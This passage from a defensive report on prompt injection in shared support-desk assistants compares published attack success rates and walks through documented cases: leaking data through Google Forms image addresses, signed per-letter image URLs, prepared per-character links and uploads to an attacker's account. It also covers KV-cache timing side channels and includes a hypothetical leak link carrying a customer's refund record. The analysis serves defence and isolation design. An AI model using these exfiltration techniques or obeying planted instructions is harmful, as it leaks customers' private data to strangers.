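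Several system cards from 2026, the documents in which developers describe how they tested a new model, include rates for prompt injection. TechRepublic's *OpenAI’s GPT-5.6 Tests Show Prompt-Injection Gains and Agent Risks* explains that OpenAI calls an injection direct when a user tries to override higher-ranking instructions, and indirect when the instructions arrive in material that a tool supplies. A poisoned ticket is an indirect injection, but the most impressive figures usually concern direct ones. GPT-5.6 Sol failed against about 0.05% of direct attacks but 3.77% of indirect ones, and its sister models Terra and Luna failed against 3.32% and 2.94% of indirect attacks. According to Cross (2026), in *GPT-6 Sol Scores 97.13% on Indirect Injection Defense*, the newer GPT-6 Sol resists 99.99% of direct attacks and 97.13% of indirect ones, which implies that 2.87% of indirect attacks still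 succeed.

The models that leaked nothing in 15 guest-note trials with the booking tool could still fail in that setting about 3.3% of the time, the average of OpenAI's three figures. At that rate, 15 trials would show no leaks about 60% of the time.

Anthropic's cards are useful because they often separate results by task and number of attempts. VentureBeat covered the February card for Claude Opus 4.6 and the May card for Opus 4.8. Digital Applied (2026), an agency, went through the card for Claude Fable 5. The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection* gives the results for Opus 5, including a test run by the security firm Gray Swan.

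| Model and task | Attempts | Success rate of attacks | Reported by |
|---|---|---|---|
| Opus 4.6, writing code | 200 | 0% | VentureBeat |
| Opus 4.6, operating a screen, no safeguards | 1 | 17.8% | VentureBeat |
| Opus 4.6, operating a screen, no safeguards | 200 | 78.6% | VentureBeat |
| Opus 4.6, operating a screen, with safeguards | 200 | 57.1% | VentureBeat |
| Opus 4.8, browsing, no safeguards | rate per attempt | 31.5% | VentureBeat |
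| Opus 4.8, browsing, with safeguards | rate per attempt | 0.5% | VentureBeat |
| Fable 5, writing code | 200 per scenario | 0.41% | Digital Applied |
| Opus 5, browsing | 129 scenarios | 0% | The Decoder |
| Opus 5, Gray Swan's general test | 15 | 2.0% | The Decoder |

Newer models resist attacks better. On Gray Swan's test, attackers with 15 attempts succeeded 5.5% of the time against Opus 4.8 and 2.0% against Opus 5. In coding, the attack success rate fell from 2.09% for Opus 4.8 to 0.41% for Fable 5. In September, Anthropic described Mythos 5.1 as its most robust model so far on an external test of indirect injection.

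But the task can matter as much as the model. Opus 4.6 resisted 200 attempts while writing code, but when it was operating a screen, an attack usually succeeded within 200 attempts. None of these figures is for a model summarising a shared ticket database, and it isn't clear which row such a tool would resemble. A summariser that only reads tickets and writes text has fewer ways to go wrong than an agent clicking through a website, but almost everything it reads comes from strangers.

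Rates from different tests don't combine well either. ctsd's *GPT-6 Astra* (2026) reports that indirect attacks succeed in 8.5% of scenarios against GPT-6 Astra and 4.8% against Claude Opus 5. The Opus 5 rate is more than twice the Gray Swan figure for the same model, so the tests must have used different attacks or counted success differently. The ranking within one test is more informative. Wizwand's *Indirect Prompt Injection on LivePI Total*, a leaderboard from May 2026, lists success rates of 10.7% against Opus 4.6, 27.2% against GPT-5.3-Codex and 29.6% against Gemini 3.1 Pro. Gemini 3.1 Pro also followed planted text most often in the hotel trials. A company that picks a model for its price could easily face an attack success rate well above the best published ones.

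Much of this evidence comes from the companies selling the models, and they choose what to test. VentureBeat notes that in the tests reported in its GPT-5.5 system card, OpenAI covered one type of connection and used attacks it already knew. Outside tests are only partly independent. Dziemian, Lin and colleagues (2026) used a large public competition to study indirect injection, and their co-authors include staff of OpenAI, Anthropic, Meta and the British and American government institutes for AI security. This cooperation probably improves the tests, but it also means the developers know them well.

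### Is a low failure rate enough?

One argument for using a model that can sometimes be tricked is that companies already accept this risk with employees. Employees sometimes fall for fraudulent emails, and firms manage this with training, limits and monitoring. OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026) compares an AI agent to a customer support worker who can issue refunds. The employer expects some customers to deceive the worker, so it caps refunds and flags suspicious messages. If a model falls for fewer tricks than a person would, it seems inconsistent to reject it because its failure rate isn't zero.

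Combining defences can also help. ClawSouls' *The most exciting line was buried in a system card* quotes Anthropic's Boris Cherny as saying that a well-trained model, combined with injection detectors and the automatic safety mode in Claude Code, brings the attack success rate down to "~0". The safeguards on Opus 4.8's browser agent cut successful attacks by a factor of about 60. Real attackers also have to put effort into each attempt, and every poisoned ticket leaves a record with the provider that somebody may read and report.

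The opposing argument is that the attacker can keep trying and needs to succeed only once. If each attempt succeeds with probability *p* and the attempts are independent, the chance of at least one success in *n* attempts is

1 − (1 − *p*)ⁿ

The Decoder's *Claude Opus 4.5 resists prompt injections better than rivals* reports that a single strong attack on Claude Opus 4.5, an older model, succeeded 4.7% of the time in Gray Swan's test. From that rate, the formula predicts a success rate of 38% after ten attempts and 99% after 100, but the measured rates were 33.6% and 63%. For Opus 4.6 operating a screen, the formula predicts near-certain success after 200 attempts, but the measured rate was 78.6%.

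The formula overstates the risk from repeated attempts because they aren't independent. Some targets resist everything the attacker has, and a text that failed once will often fail again. But a single-attempt rate is much more misleading because it understates that risk. An attack on Opus 4.5 with about a one-in-twenty chance of succeeding on a single attempt was more likely than not to succeed within 100 attempts.

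The stranger with the sofa can make many attempts with little effort. A contact form accepts any number of complaints, and successes appear in the stranger's own access log, showing which wording works. One open ticket may also get several chances, since the model rereads it whenever a staff member asks for a summary. The stranger can also send the same text to many companies. If 15 tickets together have a 2% chance of succeeding at one provider, sending them to 100 similar providers should succeed at about two of them on average. The 2% comes from Gray Swan's test of Opus 5, so this is an illustration, not a forecast for help desks.

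Published rates may also omit the attacks that work best. Anthropic says human researchers consistently find more creative attacks than automated systems. OpenAI describes an email that outside researchers reported in 2025. It read like a follow-up about a company restructuring and presented sending an employee's name and address to an outside service as a normal compliance step. In testing, it worked 50% of the time when the user made one particular request. OpenAI says programs that classify incoming text don't usually catch such messages, because the task becomes as hard as "detecting a lie or misinformation". Anthropic's results with its safeguards suggest that detection can work better than this, at least in a browser. The safeguards were much less effective for Opus 4.6 operating a screen, where even with them a series of 200 attempts succeeded 57.1% of the time.

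How much an attacker gains from one success matters as much as how often attacks succeed. An assistant that leaks one delivery date in every 10,000 attempts is a nuisance, but the support assistant can read all 80 open tickets, so one successful attack could expose far more. Baig and colleagues add that operators can't measure a deployment's failure rate once and rely on it, because the rate changes when the supplier updates the model. The GPT-5.6 models did better than GPT-5.4-mini, but the next update may not be an improvement.

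The argument that the risk is manageable therefore works best for tools that have a small reach and give strangers few chances to retry. A tool that summarises several customers' tickets doesn't meet either condition. OpenAI says that its models refuse most of the attacks it sees, but it also checks the addresses ChatGPT opens, to protect against attacks that have already manipulated the model.

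## Link rules in deployed products and how they have been bypassed

A link rule limits which web addresses an assistant may open or include in its answers. The software around the model enforces the rule, so it still applies when the model follows an injected instruction. A list of permitted domains stopped every leak in the experiment by Lan and colleagues. Commercial products need longer lists and can send requests in more ways, and researchers have found gaps in several of their rules. These cases concern how data leaves a product, and a link rule can't keep one tenant's records out of a context that another tenant's ticket also enters.

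### Image policies and the domains they permit

In a content security policy, the line `img-src cdn.support.example` lets the page load images only from that domain. If the model writes an image address on the attacker's server, the browser never sends the request, however well the attacker has disguised the data. The line doesn't affect links the user clicks, previews in a chat program, or pages an agent opens itself.

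The policy also can't restrict the query part of an address, so data can still go to any permitted domain, and on some of those domains anybody can set up a page that collects it. In 2023, Google's chat assistant Bard loaded images only from Google's own domains. Willison explains in *Hacking Google Bard* that this didn't stop a leak, because anybody can run a small program on `script.google.com`. Embrace The Red's *Exfiltrating Your ChatGPT Chat History and Memories With Prompt Injection* describes a similar gap in ChatGPT, where an early link check accepted addresses on a Microsoft domain for rented cloud storage on which the researcher had an account.

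The email program Superhuman permitted images from `docs.google.com`, which also hosts Google Forms. The address of a form can contain answers, and opening that address submits them. PromptArmor's *Superhuman AI Exfiltrates Emails*, from January 2026, describes how an attacker could use this. The attacker creates a form and sends the victim an email with instructions for the model. The victim doesn't open it, but asks Superhuman's assistant to summarise recent mail. The assistant copies text from other emails into the form's address and writes the address as an image. The browser requests the image because Superhuman permits the domain, and Google records the text as a response to the attacker's form. A single answer could leak the full text of several emails, or parts of more than 40.

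The attacker needed only a free web form, with no server or domain. PromptArmor reported the flaw on a Friday night, and Superhuman disabled the affected features the following Monday. A stricter image policy would not have been enough, because the assistant could also open any web page to look up an answer. PromptArmor showed that an injected instruction could make it open a page on the attacker's domain, with the emails in the URL.

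A list of permitted domains can also limit an agent's browsing, but how well it protects data depends on which domains it includes. Willison, in *45 posts tagged “exfiltration-attacks”*, discusses Antigravity, a coding tool that Google released with such a list in November 2025. The default list included `webhook.site`, which records incoming requests and shows them to whoever set up the address. Developers use it for testing, which may be why it was included.

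### Image proxies and link removal

An image proxy is a server that fetches images for the browser, so the browser only has to contact the proxy. If the proxy fetches any address it receives, it passes the data on to the attacker, as Bing did in SearchLeak. GitHub's proxy, Camo, therefore accepts only addresses with a valid signature, which a model can't calculate for an address it has just made up.

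Legit Security's *CamoLeak* describes an attack that obtained the signatures in advance. The researcher used GitHub's programming interface to create a signed image address for every letter and symbol he needed. An injected instruction then made GitHub's assistant, Copilot Chat, spell out private text as a series of these images. Copilot added a random number to the end of each address so that browser caching didn't block repeated letters. In the demonstrations, the attack leaked the description of an undisclosed security flaw from a private project and the results of a search of the victim's code for a cloud access key. GitHub had turned off images in Copilot Chat by 14 August 2025, which fixed the problem.

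Some products check the links in an answer before anyone sees it. Glean's *Untrusted URL monitoring* describes this check in a workplace assistant that searches a company's data. The software compares every link with sources the administrator trusts. Depending on the settings, it either records an untrusted link and leaves it in the answer, or replaces it with a placeholder if the severity is at least medium.

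For a support desk, the riskiest setting concerns links that a tool has returned. An administrator can trust all of these, on the reasoning that the model didn't invent them. But the tool in the sofa example is the ticket database, and the stranger wrote the ticket. If the administrator trusts that tool and chooses to match links by domain, one mention of the stranger's domain in the complaint makes every address on it acceptable, including the one with Maria Lind's refund. Matching by full address removes that link, because the model added the refund to whatever the ticket contained. (Glean always lets addresses ending in `.example` through, since they lead nowhere, but a real attacker would use another ending.)

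### When many customers share the permitted domain

Claude Cowork, Anthropic's agent for office work, runs code in a virtual machine, a simulated computer separate from the user's own. Code in the machine can contact only a short list of domains, which has to include `api.anthropic.com` because Cowork needs Anthropic's models to work.

PromptArmor's *Claude Cowork Exfiltrates Files* appeared in January 2026, two days after the product's release. In the demonstration, the victim gave Cowork a document containing hidden instructions and the attacker's API key. Without asking for approval, Cowork used the key to upload the victim's largest file, a loan estimate with partial social security numbers, to the attacker's account on Anthropic's file service. PromptArmor used the small model Claude Haiku, but also got Opus 4.5, which resists injections better, to leak customer records the same way.

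Embrace The Red's *Claude Pirate* described the route in October 2025, before Cowork existed. Anthropic closed that report, then acknowledged on 30 October that it should have accepted it, but the route was still open more than two months later.

Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products* (May 2026) says that the company's engineers had thought of the list as a filter on destinations, but listing a domain allowed every function available there, including uploads to any customer's account. Anthropic added a proxy inside the virtual machine that lets a request through only if it carries the token issued for that session. The check has to happen there because, on Anthropic's servers, a request from Cowork looks like one from any other program.

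This leak moved data from the victim's computer to the attacker's account, and both were customers of Anthropic. It is only a partial example of the leak between tenants, because Claude had only the victim's files in its context and the data left in an upload rather than a link.

The support provider has the same problem with its own domain. Suppose it hosts help pages for all its customers at `support.example` and shows each customer the full addresses that visitors to its pages requested. Almost any link rule would permit this domain, since the assistant has to be able to link to help articles. The assistant could then write this address:

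`support.example/furniture-shop/help?note=refund-88213-maria-lind`

After a click, the furniture shop would find the hotel guest's refund in its visitor statistics. A contact form with pre-filled answers or a report on which links people clicked would work the same way. If the provider offers free trials, an outsider can become a tenant within minutes. This attack is hypothetical, but Google Forms and Anthropic's file service are also shared services in which the account named in the request determines who gets the data.

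Giving each tenant a separate subdomain, such as `furniture-shop.support.example`, helps only if the link rule distinguishes between subdomains. In Glean, an administrator who trusts a domain also trusts all its subdomains. PromptArmor's *One Key Way Salesforce Mitigates AI Risk* advises against allowing a whole group of sites with one entry if any of them hosts content from users. A safer rule for the support provider would permit only the help pages of the tenant whose ticket the assistant is working on. Like Anthropic's repair, this rule would check the account as well as the domain.

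Freshdesk, a support desk that many companies share, lets an administrator list trusted domains. When a human staff member's message links to any other domain, Freshdesk warns them or prevents them from sending it. This could keep the stranger's link out of a reply to a customer, but it wouldn't catch the link to the furniture shop's help page if the provider's domain is on the list.

### Rules for complete addresses

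A rule can instead compare the whole address, which prevents the model from adding data after a permitted domain. OpenAI reached its current rule in stages. Embrace The Red dates ChatGPT's first link check to December 2023 and notes that the macOS and iOS apps initially lacked it. By September 2025, ChatGPT opened an address only if it exactly matched one it had received, and would not add anything to it even when instructed to.

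Radware's *ZombieAgent* got around this with an email that contained a ready-made address for each letter and digit, plus one for spaces. When the user asked ChatGPT to do something in Gmail, it read the email and opened the addresses that spelled out private data. OpenAI's servers made the requests before the user saw any answer. Radware also prepared a separate set of addresses for each position in the text, so that an attacker could reconstruct it even if the requests arrived out of order. Ten positions take 360 addresses for letters and digits.

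Radware reported the attack on 26 September 2025, and OpenAI fixed it 81 days later. The earlier rule checked whether the model changed an address, but the attacker supplied addresses that needed no changes. According to *ChatGPT falls to new data-pilfering attack as a vicious cycle in AI*, an Ars Technica article, ChatGPT now opens a link from an email only if the link appears in a public index or the user has supplied it.

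Under OpenAI's January 2026 rule, an agent may automatically load an address only if an independent crawler has already recorded it or it came from the user. According to Embrace The Red, an address that the user enters in a message counts as safe for the rest of the session. For any other address, the software either tells the agent to try another website or warns the user.

Embrace The Red reports that OpenAI's paper on the rule, *Preventing URL-Based Data Exfiltration in Language-Model Agents*, acknowledges that an attacker can still use one indexed page for each letter. This takes more preparation than ZombieAgent did, because the crawler must have found each page beforehand, and listing the addresses in an email is no longer enough. But an established blog may already have 36 suitable pages, and an attacker with a larger site could assign whole words to thousands of pages.

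Allowing any address that a user enters is also unsafe if the user doesn't know what they are pasting. Anthropic describes an internal exercise from February 2026 in which a researcher emailed an employee a ready-made prompt for Claude Code and persuaded them to run it. The prompt mixed ordinary set-up steps with an instruction to send login credentials to an outside server, and Claude sent them in 24 of 25 repetitions. A link rule that accepts every address in a user's message would accept an address that an attacker had put in a prompt for the user to paste.

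Anthropic uses a different test for complete addresses. According to its developer guide, *Web fetch tool*, Claude can't fetch an address that it has composed itself. The address must have appeared earlier in the conversation, in a user message, a result from the developer's own tools, or a result from an earlier search or fetch. The guide warns that some risk remains when Claude handles private data along with untrusted text. Developers can limit the number of fetches, but there is no limit by default.

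Willison thinks the ban on composed addresses provides most of the protection, because the usual attack makes the model add private data to an address. He points out that developers' software often inserts untrusted text into the user message. The support assistant is a clear example, since its tickets would arrive either in that message or as a tool result. The stranger could list 36 complete addresses in the complaint about the sofa, and Claude could fetch them all even if none had been in a public index. A newer version of Anthropic's documentation describes a setting that excludes addresses found only in the results of the developer's tools, which would close this gap if the tickets arrive as tool results.

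The attack that Ayush Paul demonstrated on Claude in July 2026 used another permitted source, the links on pages that Claude had already fetched. On his website, he claimed that AI assistants had to identify their user by browsing through profiles letter by letter, and each page had links for the next step. As Willison explains, the site showed these pages only to visitors that identified themselves as Claude, so a person checking it would have noticed nothing. Claude gave away the user's name, home city and employer. Anthropic said it had already found the problem internally, and it removed Claude's permission to follow links from fetched pages. The change makes the tool less useful for research, where following references between pages is normal.

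ZombieAgent and Paul's attack both worked because the attacker could introduce new addresses during the conversation. OpenAI's index is harder to manipulate because the crawler builds it separately. For a tool that reads strangers' tickets, a rule based on such an index is therefore better than one based on what has appeared in the context. A provider with its own summariser probably doesn't have a crawler, so the simplest equivalent is a fixed list of complete addresses for the articles its staff need.

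### Requests that never reach the rule

OpenAI's rule protects only the products that apply it. *Codex Exfiltrates Connector Data* describes an attack that PromptArmor reported on 21 April 2026, almost three months after OpenAI announced the rule. An email caused OpenAI's agent Codex to write an image address that submitted other emails to a Google Form, as in the Superhuman attack. An address containing the text of private emails would hardly have been in a public index, so Codex was evidently loading images without the check. OpenAI has since fixed this. Embrace The Red had warned of such gaps when the rule came out, because developers in a large company may not know that a protection exists.

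A rule that prevents a leak in one program can also be bypassed when a second program displays the same answer. PromptArmor's *OpenAI API Logs* shows this with a test application for checking the identity of bank customers. An injected instruction made the model write an image address containing a customer's personal data. Another model flagged the answer as suspicious, and the application never displayed it. When a developer opened the conversation in OpenAI's log viewer to investigate, the viewer loaded the image and sent the data to the attacker.

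Showing only plain text in the application would not have prevented the leak, since the log contained the model's original answer. The successful detection made the leak more likely because it gave the developer a reason to look at the log. OpenAI confirmed the flaw after PromptArmor published it, and a fix was under way by 22 January 2026. This route is obscure, but it matters for a multi-tenant service because the engineers who investigate strange answers often have access to every tenant's conversations, and they may use a viewer that nobody considered when writing the link rule.

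Cowork's network controls have a similar gap. Cloud Security Alliance's *Top 6 Claude Cowork Security Risks to Watch* notes that the web search and web fetch tools bypass these controls entirely. An administrator who sees a short list of permitted domains could easily assume that the list applies to those tools too.

### Links that wait for a click

Even when a product blocks automatic requests, a person can still click a link. OpenAI's warning tells the user that the link isn't verified, that it may include information from the conversation, and that they should make sure they trust it. The warning also shows the address and lets the user copy or open it. By March 2026, OpenAI was using the same protection, called Safe Url, for pages opened in its Atlas browser and for searches by its Deep Research agent. If Safe Url detects that information from the conversation would go to a third party,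 it either shows the user that information and asks for confirmation, or blocks the request.

Seeing the information in the warning could help the staff member in the sofa example, because "refund-88213-maria-lind" is out of place in a link about a sofa. If the model had encoded the refund as random-looking characters, the warning would be much harder to interpret. The address of a page that stands for one letter would look harmless.

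OpenAI doesn't report in either post how often people open a link despite the warning. The nearest figure comes from Anthropic, which found that Claude Code users approved about 93% of permission requests and paid less attention to each one as the number of requests grew. Most of the requests were probably harmless and approving them was correct, so this isn't an error rate. Claude Code users are also mostly developers judging commands, not support staff judging links. Still, the finding suggests that it is risky to rely on a warning that appears often.

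OpenAI similarly argues that strict domain lists cause frequent false alarms, which teach people to click through warnings. Its own rule could cause the same problem at a support provider. Public crawlers can't see pages behind a login, such as tickets and customer dashboards, so a public index would not contain the internal links that staff use all day. Without an exception for those pages, staff could get so many warnings that they ignore the one about a stranger's link. Anthropic reduced Claude Code's permission requests by 84% by enforcing limits in software and letting it work within them without asking.

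Salesforce's Trusted URLs lets an administrator, rather than the person reading the answer, decide which external addresses an agent can use. According to TechNadu's *Salesforce to Enforce Trusted URLs for Agentforce and Einstein AI*, agents have been able to write or call only approved external addresses since 8 September 2025. PromptArmor recommends adding addresses individually and using the same settings page to block images from domains that don't need to supply them.

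For a tool that handles several customers' records, having an administrator approve addresses in advance is safer than asking staff to judge each link. An administrator has time to find out who can publish on a site and who can read its logs, while a staff member has to decide in the middle of a ticket. However, the agent can't link to a new supplier's instructions until somebody has approved the address. Somebody also has to keep the list up to date, since the ForcedLeak attack succeeded through an approved domain that had expired.

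### The sofa ticket under each rule

Suppose the provider applies one link rule at a time to the assistant that summarises its 80 open tickets, and that each time the model follows the stranger's instruction and tries to send details of Maria Lind's refund to the stranger's server.

| Rule | Effect on the stranger's address | What can still get out |
|---|---|---|
| Image policy | Blocks it as an image but not as a link | Whole records, after a click or through a permitted site that collects data |
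| Proxy with signed image addresses | Blocks it as an image but not as a link | Whole records after a click, and short secrets through one signed image per letter |
| Link removal, matched by domain | Leaves it in place if the ticket database is a trusted source | Whole records, after a click |
| Link removal, matched by full address | Removes it | Short secrets, if the ticket supplies complete addresses and its database is trusted |
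| Domain list for an agent | Blocks the agent's request | Whole records, through a permitted domain where the stranger has an account |
| OpenAI's public index | Blocks the automatic request or warns the user | Short secrets through indexed pages, and whole records if the user continues |
| Anthropic's web fetch rule | Blocks the agent's request | Short secrets through addresses in the ticket, and whole records if the staff member clicks a link in the answer |
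| Advance approval by an administrator | Blocks it | Whole records, through an approved site whose data the stranger can read |

The outcome is different when the leak is accidental. For example, the model might write a link that searches the manufacturer's forum for B's printer fault but includes a contact from A's ticket. A domain list would probably permit the link because the forum is reputable. OpenAI's rule would treat it as unverified, since a crawler is unlikely to have recorded a search for that contact. Checking the complete address therefore works better against accidental leaks than checking the site's reputation.

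No link rule stops A's data from reaching C in plain text. The data could appear in the staff member's reply, or in an answer to C's own employees if they can use the assistant and it retrieves A's ticket for them. Salesforce also offers masking, which replaces sensitive data with placeholders before the model receives it. A placeholder could protect Maria Lind's name in both a reply and a link if the software doesn't put the name back into the finished answer. But C could still learn that the hotel group owes a guest a refund, unless the software keeps A's ticket out of the context.

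## Designs that keep customers' data apart

The simplest protection against a leak between customers is to put only one customer's data in each context. If the assistant can't see customer A's tickets while it works on customer C's, a stranger's instruction in one of C's tickets can't get A's data into a link or a reply, even if the model follows it. Links still need to be restricted, because the instruction could
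leak a detail from another of C's tickets.

Most support work fits this design, because each ticket belongs to one tenant and the software can start the next ticket with an empty context. *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* (Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues, 2025) suggests something similar for a furniture shop's chatbot, which shouldn't be able to reach another customer's data during a session. The design is less convenient for staff, who must ask twice and compare the answers themselves if they want to know whether A has the same fault as C.

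### Taking the tenant from the login

A session for customer C protects customer A only if the model can't change the session's tenant. The hotel system that Baig and colleagues describe therefore takes the permitted tenants from a signed login token. If a model adds a tenant to the token, the signature no longer matches and the server refuses the request. The gateway in front of the server also deletes any identity details that a program puts elsewhere in its request.

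How the system reads the token also affects security. During development, the team found that Python's usual pattern for a digit also accepts digits from other scripts. Two group names could therefore look different to an administrator but give access to the same tenant, if one was written in Arabic-Indic digits. The system now accepts only the digits 0 to 9, without leading zeros.

The token alone doesn't protect A when a staff member is allowed to read several tenants' tickets, because the hotel design lets an agent list its user's tenants and select one. It would be safer for the software to set the tenant from the ticket the staff member opened and issue a token for only that tenant before the model reads anything.

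### Filtering rows inside the database

With row-level security, the database adds the tenant filter to every query. On a connection opened for C, a request for all open tickets returns 15 rows instead of 80, even if a programmer forgot the filter or the model wrote the query. The protection depends on which account the agent uses, and in the Supabase demonstration the agent's key bypassed the filter.

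PostgreSQL and SQL Server have row-level security, but MySQL, which the hotel system uses, does not. Baig and colleagues describe two substitutes. In the first, which is stronger, the agent's database account can read only filtered views of the tables, and a query that names an underlying table fails with an error. The second sends every query through one piece of application code that always adds the filter. The hotel system used the second because changing the production database required an approval the team didn't yet have. Any program that connects without going through that code can read every tenant's rows.

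A query that filters only its main table can still expose another tenant's data. Suppose a guest first registers at one hotel and later books a room at another. The booking belongs to the second hotel, but the guest's record belongs to the first. A query that filters the bookings and then looks up each guest returns names and telephone numbers that the second hotel doesn't own. In the relationship between tables where this was most common, 15.72% of rows crossed a tenant boundary. In another relationship from the same table, only about 0.0014% did, so a developer could easily test that one and find nothing. The team's original audit log couldn't show these crossings either, because it recorded only the main table in each query. The design now applies the tenant condition to every table a query touches.

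These percentages describe one company's database and show how much the unfiltered query could have exposed. The team calculated them without running the query. Such a leak doesn't require an injected instruction, and the result would look like an ordinary list of guests.

Filtering by several tenants at once can also be slow. A database uses an index, like the one in a book, to find one tenant's rows quickly. Some filters wrap the tenant column in a function, which makes the database read the whole index. Baig and colleagues timed four ways of filtering one large table by three tenants.

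| Way of filtering | Median time |
|---|---|
| Function that searches a JSON list | 5,781 ms |
| Function that searches a comma-separated list | 1,330 ms |
| Join with a small table of permitted tenants | 101 ms |
| Tenants written directly into each query | 81 ms |

The slowest method returned the same results as the join but took 57 times as long. Writing the tenants directly into each query is slightly faster than the join, but the application then has to build the filter every time, a step the stronger design is meant to remove.

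The filter that the hotel system used in production also slowed down suddenly, from about 1.1 seconds for ten tenants to 10 seconds for fifteen, because the database switched to a less suitable index. The filtered views were both safer and faster in this system, taking 1.5 seconds for twenty tenants. Adding a missing index would probably remove much of the filter's delay, but the team couldn't test that on its read-only copy.

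Reused connections can cause leaks that are harder to notice. If a connection still carries A's scope when the system reuses it for C's request, the database's filter works correctly but selects A's data instead of C's, and nothing in the log looks unusual. The hotel system avoids this by opening a new connection for each request. Opening one took 638 milliseconds, about 21 times as long as a typical query, though the measurement included a private network link that other systems wouldn't need. Resetting the scope whenever a connection changes hands would be much faster, but a faulty reset would cause the same leak.

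Database filters stop data from crossing between tenants, but not from leaving through a link.

### Copies outside the database

An assistant often finds tickets through a search index, which stores a numerical description of each text so that software can retrieve the texts closest in meaning to a question. If all tenants share an index, a question about C's unpaid refunds could retrieve Maria Lind's ticket, because both concern unpaid refunds. *Systematization of Knowledge* (Gaire, Gyawali and colleagues, 2025), a survey of security in the Model Context Protocol, recommends dividing search indexes by tenant, switching off caches shared between users, and having every component check a token that identifies the tenant. Separate indexes take more work to maintain, but if someone forgets to filter a search by tenant, it still returns nothing from another tenant.

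The assistant's saved notes should also belong to a tenant, not to a member of staff. Suppose the assistant saves a note on Monday that A's refund 88213 is still unpaid. On Tuesday the same staff member opens a ticket from C, and the software loads the assistant's notes into the context. The context now contains A's data, even though the database returned only C's rows. A planted instruction could persist in the same way. Gaire and colleagues warn that malicious material can survive from one session to another through shared files. The drawback of separating notes by tenant is that staff lose an assistant that remembers solutions from other customers.

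Developers can also copy one tenant's data into every context by hand, by using a real request as a worked example in the model's instructions. tianpan.co's *Tenancy Leaks Through Few-Shot Examples* describes a developer who finds a request the product handled badly, pastes a corrected version into the standing instructions and releases the update to all customers. The model may then repeat a name or ticket number from the example when another tenant asks something similar. The article is one engineer's argument and has no measurements, but the mechanism is plausible, and a database filter can't detect it. Invented examples avoid the problem but tend to work less well than real ones.

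### Shared model caches

A cache of a model's intermediate calculations, like the one in the Cloudflare incident, can reveal text even when it works correctly. If two requests begin with the same words, the server can reuse its calculations for those words, so the later request finishes sooner. An attacker who notices the faster response learns that somebody else recently sent the same words.

In *I Know What You Asked*, Wu, Zhang and colleagues (2025) turned this into a way to read prompts. Their attack targets SGLang, a serving program that prioritizes the waiting request with the longest beginning already in the cache. The attacker guesses the next word or part of a word, sends many candidates among dummy requests, and watches which one the server answers early, since that one matches the victim's text. Repeating this recovers the prompt piece by piece.

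On a 13-billion-parameter model running on one graphics processor, the attack recovered all or part of the prompt in 95% of cases with no prior knowledge. When the attacker knew the fixed instructions and wanted only the user's input, it succeeded in 99% of cases. A customer of the support provider could know these instructions, because they are the same for everyone's tickets. One input, a person's sex, age, weight and height, took 60 requests to recover, but the average was roughly 950 to 3,100, depending on the type of prompt. Wu and colleagues ran their tests on their own machine, whereas in a large cloud the attacker's request may reach a different processor from the victim's. The attack also recovered less text when more than 200 people were using the server.

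Sharing a cache between users was common in 2024. *From Models to Services* (2026), a survey of security in hosted models, reports an audit of 17 commercial providers in the second half of that year. The auditors detected caching at eight providers, seven of which shared the cache between users. *Where the Savings Go* (Sun and Xiao, 2026) reports that commercial services now keep a separate cache for each organisation, workspace or account.

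That may not help the support provider's customers. The provider probably has one account with the model company and sends A's, B's and C's tickets through it, so all three share a cache. Sun and Xiao point out that resellers and applications commonly serve many people through one account.

They also show that hiding the faster answer doesn't close the leak. When the server skips work for a cached text, every request waiting behind it also moves forward. The attacker surrounds a guessed text with small requests of their own and counts the processing steps until the small requests finish. In tests with recorded traffic on a single server at up to half its capacity, one attempt revealed whether a text of at least 256 tokens (roughly 190 English words) was in the cache. The rate of "cached" results was at least 98 percentage points higher when the text was there than when it wasn't. The attacker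 can use this to confirm that A sent a particular standard letter, but not to read a ticket whose text they don't already know.

Sun and Xiao recommend adding a secret value for each tenant to the key under which the server stores its calculations, so that identical texts from A and C no longer match. The support provider would have to supply this value, since the model company doesn't know which tenant a request belongs to. Separate caches slow the service down. *Selective KV-Cache Sharing to Mitigate Timing Side-Channels in LLM Inference* (2025) found that giving each user a separate cache increased the wait for the first piece of an answer by 2.3% to 8.9% for a 13-billion-parameter model and by 8.3% to 38.9% for a 70-billion-parameter model. That delay seems acceptable for confidential tickets. The protection only covers leaks between tenants, and a rule about links wouldn't help here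 because the attacker doesn't need a link.

### Summarising across tenants in two stages

Some tasks need data from more than one tenant. For example, a support manager who asks what went wrong this morning wants an answer drawn from all 80 open tickets.

The simplest solution is to write each customer's summary in a separate context and show all three on one page. If C's summary contains the stranger's link, the link can carry only C's data. This keeps A's and B's data out of the link, but C's data can still leak through it. And because no context contains both A's and B's data, no model can detect that they have the same fault.

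Beurer-Kellner and colleagues describe a stricter arrangement, which they call the map-reduce pattern after an older method of splitting up large computations. Isolated model calls each read some of the untrusted text and return an answer in a restricted format, and a separate step combines the answers. For the 80 tickets, it could work like this:

1. Ordinary code fetches the tickets and starts one model call per tenant. A's call receives 40 tickets, B's 25 and C's 15. None of the calls has any tools.
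2. For each ticket, the call returns a type of problem from a list of five and either "urgent" or "not urgent".
3. The code rejects any value that isn't on the lists and counts the rest.
4. Another model receives only the counts and writes a paragraph about them.
5. The chat window shows the paragraph as plain text and doesn't turn anything in it into a link or an image. The code adds a button for each tenant's ticket list, using addresses stored in advance.

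The final model might receive these counts:

| Tenant | Payment | Delivery | Login | Equipment | Other | Total | Urgent |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| A | 14 | 0 | 11 | 9 | 6 | 40 | 5 |
| B | 7 | 0 | 12 | 5 | 1 | 25 | 3 |
| C | 4 | 8 | 1 | 0 | 2 | 15 | 1 |
| All | 25 | 8 | 24 | 14 | 9 | 80 | 9 |

Maria Lind's refund is one of A's 14 payment problems, and only A's call receives her name. C's call reads the stranger's complaint and may obey it, but has no field in which to write a link. At worst, it misreports C's 15 tickets. The final model never reads the complaint. Even if somebody later displayed the final model's paragraph in a program that creates links, an address could contain the counts but not the refund.

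The design therefore addresses both halves of the leak without relying on any model to resist an injection, but the format must be strict. A free-text field such as "short description" would let the stranger's sentence through to the final model. Restricted fields can also carry hidden messages. Five types and two levels of urgency give ten combinations, so six tickets can encode any six-digit code. In this example, the software adds up the choices and shows the result only to staff, which makes such a message hard to send and useless to the stranger. A provider that published the fields for each ticket would lose that protection.

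One call per ticket would be safer still, because the complaint could then change only its own classification, but it would take 80 calls instead of three. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues choose one call per review for product reviews, so a review written to manipulate the model can do no more than a well-written false review.

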